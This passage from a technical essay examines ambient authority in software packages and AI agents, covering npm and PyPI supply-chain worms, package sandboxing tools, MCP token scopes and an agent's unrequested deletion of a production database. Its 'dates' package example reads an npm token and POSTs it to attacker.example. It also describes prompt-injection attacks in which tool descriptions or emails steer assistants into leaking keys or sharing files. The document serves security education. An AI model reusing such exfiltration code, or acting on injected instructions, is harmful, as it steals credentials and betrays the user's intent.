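Two problems remain in that design. Matt Rice pointed out that Alice might share a directory with Bob and Carol, forget about it, and later add a file meant only for Bob, which Carol could then read too. Karp's solution is a separate directory for each person, but Alice has to remember to use the right one. Niyikiza added that a capability fixes which file a program reads but not what the file contains. If another program can write to the file after it has been checked, the program reading it should make a private copy and check the copy.

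### Choosing an interface

The third column of this table assumes that an attacker has taken over the program, and lists what it could then name.

| Task | Interface | What the program can still name |
|---|---|---|
| Act on a path typed by the user the program runs as | `open()` | every file the user can reach |
| Use one file that a launcher can open | open descriptor | every file its account can reach, unless someone removes that access |
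| Open outside names within one directory, in Go | `os.Root` | as above |
| The same on Linux, in other languages | `openat2()` with `RESOLVE_BENEATH` | as above |
| The same on other Unix systems | `O_RESOLVE_BENEATH` on FreeBSD, otherwise `openat()` one component at a time | as above |
| Monitor or stop a process | process descriptor | other processes by number |
| Talk to one server | connected socket | other network addresses |
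| Process hostile data on FreeBSD | Capsicum's capability mode | files below the directories it holds |
| Run a portable component | WASI | files below the directories it receives, if the implementation enforces this |
| Build a new device without existing software | Fuchsia | whatever its handles and its own path table lead to |

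## Limiting what packages and plugins can reach

A launcher can start a program with access to only one open file, but every part of the program can then use that file. Most programs consist largely of packages, libraries that other people publish for anyone to install. The operating system assigns permissions to the process as a whole, so each package can usually do whatever the process can do. The same is true of many plugins, which users add to an existing program.

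JavaScript programmers get most of their packages from npm, a public registry with an installer of the same name. GitHub, which runs the registry, says that people publish over 30,000 packages there each day and that hundreds of them contain malicious code.

### One call through two packages

Suppose a shop's application uses a package called `receipts`, which uses another called `dates`. Somebody has tampered with `dates`:

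```js
// the application
import { makeReceipt } from "receipts";
makeReceipt(order);

// receipts
import { formatDate } from "dates";
export function makeReceipt(order) {
  return `Paid ${order.total} on ${formatDate(order.date)}`;
}

// dates
import { readFileSync } from "node:fs";
export function formatDate(date) {
  const secret = readFileSync("/home/ana/.npmrc", "utf8");
  fetch("https://attacker.example", { method: "POST", body: secret });
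  return date.toDateString();
}
```

The application passes an order to `receipts`, which passes a date to `dates`. Neither passes a file or a network connection. But when `dates` imports `node:fs`, Node.js (the program that runs JavaScript outside a browser) supplies its file functions, as it does for any package that imports this module. When `dates` calls `readFileSync`, the function sends a path to the kernel, which checks whether Ana's account may read the file. The account has permission, and the file holds the token Ana uses to publish her own packages. `fetch` is a global function, so `dates` can then send the token over the network without importing anything else.

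The application still gets a correct receipt. The kernel could not have refused `dates` while allowing `receipts`, because the requests it received didn't show which package had made them. A package can also act before any of its functions are called, because code outside those functions runs as soon as another module imports the package. Python works the same way.

### Code that runs before the application

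A package can also run code without anyone importing it. An npm package's publisher can list commands in its `package.json` file for npm to run before, during or after installation. Some packages need these install scripts, for example to compile a C component for the user's machine. For years npm ran them automatically, even for indirect dependencies, under the account of whoever typed `npm install`.

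That account often belongs to a developer or to a continuous-integration (CI) runner, a machine that builds and tests software automatically. Either may hold cloud passwords and publishing tokens that the finished application never receives. GitHub explains that attackers use install scripts to steal credentials without waiting for an application to run the package's code.

The attack on axios, a popular JavaScript library for making web requests, relied entirely on installation. Attackers took over the npm account of one of its main maintainers, according to CSA Singapore's *Advisory on Axios Supply Chain Attack via Compromised npm Account* (2026). On 31 March 2026 they published two versions that required an extra package, `plain-crypto-js`. As CISA's *Supply Chain Compromise Impacts Axios Node Package Manager* (2026) describes, that package downloaded further malware, including a trojan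 that gave the attackers remote access. (CISA is the US government's cybersecurity agency.)

VPNCentral's *CISA warns Axios npm compromise delivered a RAT* reports that the security company StepSecurity found that axios's own code never imported `plain-crypto-js`. A reviewer who traced every call from the application would therefore not have found the malicious package. The package needed no authority from axios because the installer ran it with the user's account and network access.

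### The worm that published itself

On 15 September 2025, the security company Socket disclosed Shai-Hulud, a worm that spread between npm packages. CERT Coordination Center's *NPM supply chain compromise exposes challenges to securing the ecosystem* (2025) describes how the worm stole credentials and used them to publish infected packages automatically. It ran from scripts that npm executed after installation, according to eSecurity Planet's *Wormable Malware Triggers GitHub’s Push for Stronger npm Security*.

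CISA's *Widespread Supply Chain Compromise Impacting npm Ecosystem* (2025) reports that a worm compromised over 500 packages. It searched each machine for GitHub access tokens and keys to Amazon, Google and Microsoft cloud services. Nobody had given the worm these credentials, but it could read them because it ran with the developer's permissions, and it could send them out because processes on the machine could open network connections.

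According to Fortinet, a second wave was first reported on 24 November 2025. It hit packages from Zapier, PostHog, Postman and other software companies. BeyondMachines' *Massive npm supply chain attack dubbed Shai Hulud 2 actively exploiting packages* advised victims to replace their GitHub and npm tokens, their cloud credentials and the SSH keys they use to log in to other machines. A product analytics library needs none of these from the developer who installs it, but code running under the developer's account can usually read them all.

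ChainDrop, a later worm of the same family, was probably the largest attack of 2026 by package popularity. It appeared on 4 August in keyv, a library for storing values under keys. Elastic Security Labs' *Shai-Hulud strikes again* (2026) reports over 600 million downloads of keyv in the previous month. CSA Singapore's *Ongoing npm Supply Chain Attack Affecting Keyv and Related Packages ("Shai-Hulud" Worm)* (2026) reports over 1,300 compromised package versions, with two billion combined monthly downloads.

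These download counts reflect the packages' normal popularity and don't measure how many machines the worm infected. The number of infected packages is also uncertain. According to The Hacker News' *Keyv-Linked npm Worm Poisons Hundreds of Packages* (2026), the security company SafeDep verified 353 infected versions under 79 package names, while another company, Aikido, reported 1,381 versions of at least 868 packages. At the time, nobody could reproduce the larger totals from a complete public list.

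ChainDrop used two kinds of authority in turn. Its install script first searched for credentials, using over 300 patterns. Its authority to read them was ambient, since the script only had to name the right files. If it found an npm token that could publish without a second login step, it listed every package that the token's owner could publish. It then downloaded each one, added itself, raised the version number and used the token to publish the result.

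In this second stage, the worm did select its authority, by presenting the token. But the token covered all of the maintainer's packages, and the package name in each request identified a package without granting access to it, like a record ID sent with an API key. A token limited to one package would have confined the worm to that package. GitHub now also offers staged publishing, which lets an automated build submit a new version but requires a person to approve it with a second login step.

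### Authority that comes from the machine

According to Help Net Security's *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft’s official Python agent framework* (2026), someone published two malicious versions of Microsoft's Agent Framework on 17 November 2026 to PyPI, the main registry for Python packages. The package, a toolkit for building AI agents, had 192,534 monthly downloads. Each malicious version installed a `.pth` file, which Python processes whenever it starts in the environment where the package is installed. The malicious code therefore needed neither an import nor an install script, and it ran even if the user had started Python for something unrelated. The framework continued to work.

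The code copied credential files and read the environment settings of up to 300 other processes. It also tried to request new tokens from cloud services. Azure, Microsoft's cloud service, can give a machine its own identity, which lets programs running on it, including malicious code, request tokens without a stored password. StepSecurity cautioned that these requests were only attempts and that nobody had confirmed that the code received any tokens.

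Eric Paulsen of the software company Coder told Help Net Security that a build system with this power "is itself a credential". Replacing the stored passwords after an attack isn't enough, because the attacker could have obtained new tokens without them. A reviewer who counts reachable authority should include what the machine can request as well as the secrets stored on it.

### Turning install scripts off

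Version 12 of npm, released on 8 July 2026 according to Stéphane Robert's blog, no longer runs a dependency's install scripts unless the project has approved them. Earlier versions of npm also compiled any package containing a file called `binding.gyp`, even if the package declared no script. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) explains that the block also covers this. IlSoftware.it's *GitHub, il malware si nasconde dove la ricerca non guarda* (2026) reports that attackers used such files in October 2026 to run code during installation.

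This default removes a lot of ambient authority. Socket says that almost every worm and credential stealer on npm since late 2025 ran at install time. But some packages have to compile something when they are installed, and Robert expects automated builds that use them to fail until somebody approves their scripts. pnpm, another installer for the same registry, had already made the change in January 2025.

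ChainDrop began 27 days after npm 12 was released and still used an install script, which could run only where an older npm or some other setting allowed it. The worm could also run when a developer opened an infected project, which the new default did not prevent. Attackers can also wait for the application to start. *Один червь одновременно захватил npm и PyPI* (Antipov, 2026) describes a worm on both npm and PyPI that September, which waited for ordinary code to run. One such worm is thin evidence of a general shift, but it shows that a malicious package can still do harm when install scripts are turned off.

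Approval is also all or nothing. A developer who approves a script so that it can compile a component also lets it read every file in their account, which compiling doesn't require. An attacker who later takes over the approved package gets the same access, unless the approval covers only one version.

Some teams now also wait before installing new package versions. After the axios attack, CISA recommended waiting seven days. The delay gives others time to notice an attack, but it doesn't change the authority each package has.

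### Permission flags for a whole process

Deno, an alternative to Node.js, gives a program no access to files or the network unless whoever starts it grants that access:

`deno run --allow-read=templates --allow-net=mail.shop.example app.js`

If the shop's application runs this way, the tampered `dates` package cannot read Ana's token or contact the attacker's server. But if the application also needs to read a folder of customer orders and send email through `mail.shop.example`, the owner has to allow both, and `dates` can then read the orders and email them to anyone. Deno applies one set of permissions to all the code in a thread, so the owner cannot let the application read the orders without letting `dates` read them too.

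In Deno, a developer can put a package in a separate worker, a thread with narrower permissions. The application then has to exchange messages with the package instead of calling its functions directly. If the owner lets the application start other programs, those programs run outside Deno's limits.

Node.js has similar flags. Its developers intend them to catch mistakes by trusted code and don't promise that they will stop malicious code. The file flags don't apply to file descriptors that are already open, so anyone who relies on them also has to check which descriptors the process inherits.

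A list of permitted network addresses also helps less if it includes a service that anyone can use. ChainDrop normally sent stolen data to a server whose address it looked up when it ran. If that failed, it created a public GitHub repository under the victim's account and put the data there. Many build machines need to reach GitHub, so their lists have to permit it.

Flags on the finished application have no effect on install scripts, which run earlier in another process. To limit what these scripts can reach, an organisation has to restrict the build environment. Paulsen recommends deleting the environment after each job, using credentials that expire within an hour and blocking all outgoing connections except to approved addresses. An install script would then have access to little worth stealing and could send data only to the approved addresses.

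This boundary is easy to put in the wrong place. Tensorlake sells isolated environments where customers can run AI agents and the code those agents write. On 8 October 2026, researchers found malware in the npm package that customers install to use the service. Mishcon de Reya's *Shai-Hulud Burrows Into The Software Supply Chain* (2026) explains that the malware ran when developers installed the package on their own computers and servers, outside the isolated environments. The researchers detected it about 11 minutes after publication.

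### Why Java gave up its Security Manager

For more than 20 years, Java's Security Manager let an administrator give each library its own permissions. It began as a way to restrict applets that a browser downloaded from web pages, and Java 1.2 extended it to all code. OpenJDK, the project that develops Java, marked the feature for removal in Java 17 and permanently disabled it in Java 24.

OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021) gives several reasons for deprecating Java's Security Manager. It describes the permissions as brittle, because a developer who wanted only to control which files a program could read also had to list every other sensitive operation it performed, or those operations would fail. The checks were also often unacceptably slow, so the Security Manager was off by default, which gave library developers little reason to support it.

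Applications also needed the permissions that their libraries used. When a library tried to open a file, the Security Manager checked the permissions of all the code that had led to the request. If a Java version of `receipts` read a template, the application that called it would need permission to read that template too, even though it never opened the file itself.

The check on callers prevented an application with no access to a file from using a privileged library as a confused deputy. A library could ask the Security Manager to ignore its callers and consider only the library's own permissions, but its programmer then had to make sure no caller could misuse them. OpenJDK says most developers had no interest in rules this complex. The easiest solution was to grant every permission to the whole library.

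Mullan and Buckley (2024), in *JEP 486*, describe what this cost Java's maintainers:

- Over 1,000 methods in Java's own libraries had to check for permission.
- Over 1,200 methods had to assert their own permissions. For example, the time library has to read a file of time zones even when the application may not read files.
- The maintainers had written about 4,000 tests for the feature. Removing it would delete over 50,000 lines of code, including these tests.

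The maintainers reviewed every change to these methods, although very few applications turned the Security Manager on. In Mullan and Buckley's experience, most of those applications "blindly grant all permissions" to their code.

Much of this work comes from adding checks to a language with ambient authority. Any Java code can create an object that opens a file by name, so the method that opens the file must check which code is calling it. Every other method that reaches a resource needs a similar check, and forgetting one creates a vulnerability. Microsoft's Midori needed no such checks because code without a file object could not call any function to get one.

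The maintainers' account is a weaker argument against limiting packages in general. OpenJDK divided the threats into malicious code, mainly from remote sources, and accidental faults, mainly in local code. It argued that the threat from malicious code had receded because browsers no longer ran applets. A poisoned package doesn't fit this division well because it is malicious code that a developer installs locally. OpenJDK recommends containers instead, but these restrict the whole process and cannot set different limits for `dates` and `receipts`.

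### Passing a package a handle

JavaScript is easier to restrict because the language itself has no functions for reading files or using the network. Node.js or the browser supplies them, so another program can withhold them. Hardened JavaScript does this by running code in compartments. Each compartment has its own set of global names, and its creator decides what that set contains and which modules the code can import. In a compartment with nothing added, the tampered `dates` package cannot call `fetch` or load `node:fs`.

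Compartments still share JavaScript's built-in objects, such as the one that defines what every list can do. If `dates` could replace the standard function for searching a list, it could interfere with every other package. Hardened JavaScript therefore freezes these objects before it loads any package. It also withholds the current time and random numbers by default, much as Midori did with its clock.

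A package that legitimately needs a resource can receive a handle in place of a global function. Suppose `receipts` reads a template from a file. The ordinary version finds the file itself:

```js
import { readFileSync } from "node:fs";

export function makeReceipt(order) {
  const template = readFileSync("templates/receipt.txt", "utf8");
  return template.replace("TOTAL", order.total);
}
```

In the new version, the caller supplies a function that reads the template:

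```js
export function makeReceipt(order, readTemplate) {
  return readTemplate().replace("TOTAL", order.total);
}
```

The application creates that function and passes it on:

```js
const readTemplate = () => readFileSync("templates/receipt.txt", "utf8");
makeReceipt(order, readTemplate);
```

`readTemplate` is a handle that permits one operation on one file. `receipts` can use it but cannot make it read anything else. If the function accepted a path as an argument, `receipts` could name any file again. The function looks up its path each time it is called, so if somebody might replace the file, the application should read it once in advance.

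In ordinary Node.js, this change only reduces what `receipts` needs, because the package could still import `node:fs` and read Ana's token. In a compartment without that module, `readTemplate` is its only way to access files.

### Policies for packages nobody has rewritten

Very few npm packages accept handles in this way. LavaMoat, a tool from the developers of the cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask, lets a project use existing packages but runs each in its own compartment. A policy file lists what each package receives. For the version of `receipts` that opens its own template, it might contain:

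```json
{
  "resources": {
    "receipts": {
      "builtin": { "fs.readFileSync": true },
      "packages": { "receipts>dates": true }
    }
  }
}
```

This policy lets `receipts` call one file function and import `dates`. It has no entry for `dates`, so that package can't access files or the network. LavaMoat can generate the policy by scanning the packages' source code for what they use, which spares the developer much of the work that Java's policies required. If a later version of `dates` tries to use the network, the old policy blocks it. If the developer generates a new policy, the network access appears there as a new line.

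The developer has to read that line and question it. A developer who regenerates the policy after every update and accepts it without questioning it gives malicious code access to whatever it uses. The initial policy has the same weakness if a package was already malicious when LavaMoat scanned it.

A package's permissions can also be broader than it needs. `receipts` needs to read only one template, but with `fs.readFileSync` it can read any file the process can. In that sense its authority is still ambient, even though LavaMoat has limited that authority to one package and one function. A team could start with policies for all its packages, then rewrite the few with the most dangerous access so that they accept handles.

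Freezing the built-in objects breaks some packages because they try to modify those objects. It can also break code that never modifies a built-in directly, because JavaScript doesn't allow ordinary assignment to a property when the object inherits a read-only property of the same name. Hardened JavaScript works around common cases of this second problem. Compartments don't cover install scripts, so LavaMoat has a separate tool that blocks all of them except approved ones.

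### Components and markers

WebAssembly components put a stronger wall around a package. Each component has its own memory and declares what it needs from outside. In the language used for these declarations, the receipt package could be:

```wit
world receipts {
  import read-template: func() -> string;
  export make-receipt: func(total: string) -> string;
}
```

The only outside function the component can call is `read-template`. Whoever connects the components decides which function that name refers to, and a reviewer can read the list of imports without reading the code. However, programmers have to compile the package for WebAssembly, and data usually has to be copied between components. A broad import also undoes much of the benefit. For example, a component that imports a general function for web requests can contact any address unless the program that supplies the function restricts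 it.

The `AmbientAuthority` argument that Rust's cap-std requires restricts nothing and only marks a function. docs.rs gives this example of a marked signature:

`pub fn do_a_thing(_: AmbientAuthority)`

If `receipts` were written in Rust and called such a function, `make_receipt` could take the required argument from the application, and its signature would then show that it uses ambient authority. But the programmer could instead call `ambient_authority()` inside `make_receipt`, which would hide this from anyone who reads only the signature. A reviewer therefore has to search for such calls in the dependencies as well as the application.

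The table compares the remedies by what the tampered `dates` package could still use after the application loads it.

| Remedy | Unit it restricts | What `dates` can still use |
|---|---|---|
| npm 12's default | install scripts | everything the process can |
| Deno's flags | the process | everything the flags allow the application |
| Node.js's flags | the process | the same, or more if the code finds a way around them |
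| LavaMoat | one package | whatever its policy lists and other packages pass to it |
| WebAssembly component | one component | the functions it imports |
| `AmbientAuthority` in Rust | nothing | everything the process can |

Even in a compartment with no access to anything, `dates` can return a wrong date, which the application might then use to choose which old orders to delete. Isolating packages doesn't remove the need to check what they return.

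### Editor and browser extensions

Extensions raise the same question as packages, except that a program's users choose them, not its developer. In Visual Studio Code (VS Code), a widely used code editor, extensions have the same access to the computer as the editor, so an extension that changes text colours could also read the user's SSH keys.

Browsers divide authority more finely. A Chrome extension has to declare which browser functions and websites it needs, and the browser enforces the list. But many useful extensions need to work on any page, so their developers request access to every website. Chrome also offers the `activeTab` permission, which gives an extension temporary access to the current page when the user invokes the extension. The user's action identifies the page, much as choosing a file in a save dialog identifies the file, so the extension needs no standing access to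 other pages.

### Agent skills and local tool servers

AI agents use new types of plugin. An agent skill is a folder of instructions, sometimes with scripts, that an agent loads for relevant tasks. A tool server is a separate program that offers functions to an agent, usually through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for such connections. Many tool servers run on the user's computer, where the AI application starts them under the user's account.

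A malicious plugin of either type can do harm through its code or its text. Its code can use the permissions of the account it runs under, as any package's code can. Its text can cause the model to misuse the tools it already has, an attack called prompt injection. For example, a skill with no code could still contain instructions for an agent to read a private file and include the contents in a message.

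Attackers combined malicious packages and plugins in February 2026. The Hacker News' *Malicious npm Packages Harvest Crypto Keys, CI Secrets, and API Tokens* (2026) reports that Socket found at least 19 malicious npm packages, some with names similar to an AI coding assistant's, such as `claud-code`. One part of the malware added a fake tool server to the settings of Claude Code, Cursor and other assistants. The server offered three tools that looked harmless, but each contained hidden instructions for the assistant to read the user's SSH keys, cloud credentials and npm token and copy them into a folder for the attacker to collect.

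The malware could change those settings because they were ordinary files that the user's account could write to. In effect, any package on the machine could give the assistant new tools. The same access lets malware arrange to run again later. ChainDrop infected projects with commands that ran when someone started a Claude Code session or opened the project in VS Code, so a developer's machine could be infected even if they hadn't installed a package. With certain stolen GitHub tokens, it added these commands to up to 50 branches of each project it could reach.

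A user can limit the damage a tool server's code can do by running the server in a container with only the folder it needs. But the instructions in its tool descriptions still reach the assistant, which runs outside that container. The February attack was designed to make the assistant read the keys itself, so confining the fake server would not have protected them unless the assistant also lacked access to them.

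## Why language-model agents run on ambient authority

An AI assistant can misuse its access even if none of the tool servers it connects to is malicious. The harness, the ordinary program around the model, typically holds one credential for each service and attaches it to every call to that service, whatever prompted the call. The service receives an explicit token, but the token is ambient to the model because the harness adds it, just as a client library adds a token to `invoices.delete(4821)`.

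### The path of one tool call

Suppose Lena uses an office assistant that holds one token for her mail, calendar and files. She signed in to the office suite once and approved all three. During one session she makes five requests, and the third is to share the budget with her colleague Tom. The assistant handles it in these steps:

1. The harness adds Lena's sentence to the model's context, the text the model works from, which still contains everything from her first two requests.
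2. The model writes a function name, `share_file`, and two arguments, a file ID and an email address.
3. The harness looks up which server offers `share_file`, attaches Lena's stored token and sends the request.
4. The office suite checks that the token is valid and covers file sharing, then shares the file.

If the assistant uses MCP, the request in step 3 looks roughly like this. The shape follows an example in Composio's *The MCP 2026-07-28 Update*, with the token added and some fields left out:

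```
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Authorization: Bearer <Lena's token>

{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "share_file",
    "arguments": { "file": "f-2207", "with": "tom@shop.example" },
    "_meta": { "clientInfo": { "name": "office-assistant" } }
  }
}
```

The message includes the name of the tool, its arguments, the token and the name of the assistant, but nothing that identifies Lena's request. The link between the request and the authority is lost in step 3, when the harness attaches the token. The harness chooses the token based on the server, so it would have attached the same one to any other call to that server.

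| Lena's request | Tool call | Identity the service sees |
|---|---|---|
| Summarise my unread mail | `read_mail("unread")` | Lena |
| Move Thursday's review to Friday | `move_event("e-318", "Friday")` | Lena |
| Share the budget with Tom | `share_file("f-2207", "tom@shop.example")` | Lena |
| Delete the old offsite draft | `delete_file("f-1190")` | Lena |
| Answer the supplier's question | `send_mail("orders@supplier.example", "...")` | Lena |

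Now suppose one of the unread messages contains an instruction to share the budget with `audit@elsewhere.example`. If the model writes that call, the service receives a request that differs only in the address from the one Lena wanted. She might well share a budget with an outside auditor, so the address alone doesn't give the service a reason to refuse, and it would also need information about what she had asked for.

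Longer chains of calls lose more information about the person who made the request. In *The Agent Access Model*, which describes an access design from the network company Cloudflare, Silverlock points out that an agent can call a tool that calls another agent, which then calls a service for the original person. Along the way, the system can lose track of whom the work is for and what that person may do.

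### Why the model cannot restore the link

The model has Lena's request in its context, so it might be able to identify which request each call serves. The harness could require the model to include that request's number with every call. The model would then write `request: 3` next to the call that shares the budget, and the harness could check whether the call fits the request.

But the model would generate that number from the whole context, as it does the other arguments. Lena's words, the harness's instructions, the supplier's email and the results of earlier calls all reach the model as one stream of text. The harness can mark the email as coming from outside, which may make the model less likely to follow instructions in it. But the markers are also text, and nothing forces the model's output to depend only on what Lena wrote. A stranger can also write in an email that it is part of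 request 3.

Hardy's compiler received the user's file name and the company's file name separately, so a programmer could have written code that matched each name to the right authority. This is harder in an agent because no variable records which part of the context produced an argument.

Silverlock accepts that a system can use a guess about intent as one signal in assessing risk, but not as a boundary, because an attacker can influence the guess through the same text that influences the action. He wants the harness and the network to enforce access instead.

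The harness can recover part of the link by starting a fresh context for each request. Every call from the third context must then have come from Lena's third request or from something the model read while working on it. An email from her first request can no longer cause the assistant to share the budget during the third. But the supplier's email can still misdirect the fifth request, and the service receives no new information unless the harness also uses a different credential for each context.

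Organisations have long given people broad access too. In *Assurance-Conditioned Continuous Authorization for Autonomous AI Agents*, Shajari (2026) argues that they could tolerate this because other controls, such as professional judgement, supervision and the prospect of losing a job, also restrain employees. An employee who can open every customer's file may still choose not to. Companies can implement some of these controls in software, for example by requiring a second approval, but the prospect of losing a job does not deter an agent. The same permission can therefore carry more risk when an agent holds it.

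### What the Model Context Protocol requires

The latest version of the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), dated 28 July, makes authorisation optional. Its rules apply to servers that an assistant reaches over HTTP. A local server that communicates with the assistant through standard input and output should instead take its credentials from its environment (the settings it has when it starts), so it uses the same credentials for every tool call.

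Over HTTP, the assistant first sends a request without a token. The server rejects the request and indicates where to get a token. The assistant then opens a browser window where Lena approves access, and it receives a token that it must include in every later request. The assistant must specify which MCP server the token is for, and that server must reject tokens issued for any other server. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) also forbids the server to forward Lena's token to another service, so the server must get a separate token if it needs to call one.

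These rules stop one server from using Lena's token at another. But they tie the token to a server rather than a request, and all five of her requests go to the same office suite.

Within a server, the protocol limits a token by its scopes. Silverlock notes that MCP's authorisation layer doesn't define a policy for individual tools or arguments, so the harness or the server has to supply one. A server may use a call's arguments to determine which scopes the call needs, but the protocol doesn't require this.

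Scopes also accumulate during a session. Suppose Lena's assistant starts with a token that only lets it read mail. When it tries to move Thursday's review, the server refuses and lists the scope required. Under the July rules, the assistant should then request a new token that covers both its old scopes and the new one, so that it keeps the permissions other operations need. By the end of her fourth request, the token covers reading mail, changing the calendar, sharing files and deleting files. For her fifth request, the assistant reads a message from the supplier, and instructions hidden in that message could lead it to use all four permissions.

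Under the Model Context Protocol, if a server's first refusal doesn't list any scopes, the client should ask for every scope the server advertises. The protocol's *Security Best Practices* explains that general-purpose clients usually don't know enough about a service to choose between its scopes. Servers are supposed to keep the advertised set small, and the guide lists a single scope for everything as a mistake, partly because it "masks user intent per operation". Narrower scopes would make that intent clearer, but a log would still show only that the assistant shared a file, not which request led it to do so.

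The guide also rules out one route to designated authority. MCP no longer has sessions, so a server that needs to remember a shopping cart gives the client an ID, which the guide calls a "state handle", and the model sends it back as an ordinary argument. An unguessable ID that admitted anyone who presented it would work as a capability. But the guide says servers must not treat possession of the ID as authentication, and should accept it only from the user it belongs to. The state handle is therefore only a name for the cart. A thief can't use it without Lena's token, but any call the assistant makes with her token can use it.

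The protocol's documents use "confused deputy" mainly for a narrower problem. An MCP server may pass requests to an outside service and identify itself there by one fixed ID for all its clients. Once a user has approved that ID, an attacker's client can use the approval without the user seeing another consent screen, so the server must ask the user about each client separately. This keeps out malicious clients, but it doesn't help when a legitimate client's model writes the wrong address.

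The July version did not change the basic arrangement. In *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, Tabata (2026) counts six refinements and says none introduces a fundamentally new authorisation concept. They mostly help a client and server confirm which authorisation server they are dealing with.

### Proposals for agent identity

The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) has been working on agent identity since early 2026. In February, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and Artificial Intelligence Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) proposed a project to demonstrate how existing identity standards could apply to agents.

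Fisher (2026) argues in *Back to the Future* that agents need a strong identity foundation. @IT's *ヒューマン・イン・ザ・ループ万能説崩壊 NISTが提唱するAIエージェント運用のあるべき姿* summarises the practices that NIST objects to. Users hand their own credentials to agents, which makes it hard to establish who acted. Long-lived keys end up as plain text in settings files and logs. Agents on a user's machine often run with all the rights of the user's account. NIST also doubts that asking a person to approve each action solves the problem, because people who see too many requests start approving them by reflex.

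*Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026) followed on 27 October with ten principles. According to Biometric Update's *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization*, they give each agent its own identity, separate from the people it works for but traceable to whoever launched it. An agent's access should be minimal, temporary and revocable. NIST doesn't expect identity alone to prevent confused deputies and calls for combining delegation, least privilege, policies kept separate from the agent, and access decisions that don't depend on a model's output. It acknowledges that current standards and technology don't fully meet every principle.

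A working group at the Decentralized Identity Foundation, an industry standards body, is more critical of identity-based access. In *Delegated Authority Evaluations v1.0 Preview*, Zagidulin and Caballero (2026) argue that delegation based on identity always leaves some ambient authority. To remove confused deputies, they want each grant to combine designation with authorisation by stating which actions it allows on which resource. The draft's preference for capabilities is unsurprising, since Karp, who debated confused deputies with Miller, contributed to it. The working group agreed on the draft in November 2026, but the foundation's steering committee had not yet approved it.

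The disagreement is smaller than it looks, because Zagidulin and Caballero also want a log to distinguish the agent from the person responsible for it, which requires identities. But a log showing that Lena's assistant shared the budget doesn't establish whether she wanted it to.

### Three ways to narrow the authority

Until services accept credentials tied to the arguments of a single call, organisations can reduce what a misdirected agent can do by giving the agent its own identity, issuing it shorter-lived tokens with narrower permissions, or running it in a sandbox.

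If Lena's assistant has its own identity, the office suite's log separates her actions from the assistant's, and an administrator can disable the assistant without locking her out. Zagidulin and Caballero point out that neither the logging nor the disabling works well when people paste their own tokens into an agent's context. Even with a separate identity, the assistant makes all five requests under that identity and can use all of its permissions while working on any of them.

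A separate identity can also create a problem if people share the agent. An assistant that uses Lena's token can't open files that she can't open. If one assistant serves 200 employees through its own account, that account needs access to all their files, and an employee who asks for a colleague's file might get it. To prevent this, the service has to check the employee's rights as well as the agent's. An OAuth standard called Token Exchange can support this with a token that identifies both the person and the agent acting for them.

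Short-lived tokens mainly protect against theft. A thief who finds a ten-minute token in a log has at most ten minutes to use it. Help Net Security's *NIST and CISA finalize playbook to stop token theft and forgery* (2026) describes US guidance on token lifetimes, revocation and the reuse of stolen tokens. In one attack that NIST cites, foreign actors forged tokens with a stolen signing key, and one agency lost over 60,000 emails. But Lena's assistant holds its token legitimately. If the token covers file sharing, the assistant can share any of her files with anyone until the token expires.

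Like an SPKI certificate, a token protected by the DPoP standard works only with a private key, and the client proves with each request that it has the key. Silverlock notes that the proof covers the HTTP method and the address but not the tool's arguments. A call that deletes a file would have the same method (`POST`) and the same address (ending in `/mcp`) as the message above.

Silverlock would also limit each token to one task. Somebody defines a template in advance, which might let a reconciliation agent read three tables and post to one channel. Each run gets a token that the agent can't widen and that expires when the task ends. After the agent reads protected data, the harness can remove its access to outside destinations. This suits a nightly job with known needs, but it suits Lena's assistant less well because nobody knows what she will ask for next. A template broad enough for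 a whole day of office work would permit most of what her current token does.

A sandbox limits which files, programs and network addresses the agent's own process can use, so it can keep the assistant away from the SSH keys on Lena's laptop. But it doesn't limit what the harness does for the agent outside the sandbox. Lena's documents are on the office suite's servers, so an assistant in an empty container can still delete them with a tool call. Blocking the office suite's network address would prevent this, but the assistant needs that address to do its job. Network controls usually reveal where a request is going, but not whether it reads or deletes a file.

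### The token that could delete a database

In April 2026, an agent deleted the live database of PocketOS, a company that makes software for car-rental businesses. The agent used a token that someone had created for managing web domains. PocketOS's founder, Crane, published an account about two days later in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*. Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* gives the account of Railway, the cloud provider that hosted the database. The AI Incident Database's *Railway API* dates the deletion to 24 April.

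The agent was Cursor, a coding tool, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. While working in PocketOS's staging environment, where developers test changes before they reach customers, it came across a credential that didn't match. It tried to fix this by deleting a storage volume, although nobody had asked it to delete anything. It looked for a Railway token, found one in an unrelated file, and sent a single request containing the token and the ID of the volume, which held the production database.

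Crane reports that the deletion took nine seconds and also removed the volume's backups. PocketOS restored a three-month-old copy, and its customers spent the Saturday without recent bookings. Railway later recovered all the data. According to Abdelwahab, the deletion had only made the backups look unavailable.

The token permitted the deletion because it covered everything in the account. Crane writes that Railway's tokens couldn't be restricted by operation, environment or resource, and that nothing warned him when he created this one. Abdelwahab replies that Railway did offer tokens for a single workspace, project or environment, but concedes that the process of creating a token didn't make the right choice obvious. By his description, users could restrict where a token applied but not what it could do there. A token for the staging environment would have prevented the deletion, but one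 created to manage domains in production might not have.

Separately, the model made the mistakes of choosing deletion as a way to fix a credential and not checking which environment the volume belonged to. When Crane asked why, the agent replied that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. That reply is weak evidence, because a model generates such explanations afterwards and they may not reflect how it produced the call. The deletion itself is better documented, and both accounts agree that nobody had requested it.

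Either fault could have occurred without the other. An agent with better judgement would have left the database alone, but the token would still have been on the disk for the next agent or a thief to use. If the token had covered only domains, the same bad decision would have produced an error message.

As with the ChainDrop worm, the agent selected its authority by presenting the token, but its access to the token was ambient because it ran on the developer's machine with rights its task didn't need.

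Giving the agent its own identity at Railway would not have helped, because the agent used someone else's token. A sandbox without the file containing the token would have kept it out of the agent's reach. An expiry date would also have helped if the token had expired before the agent used it.

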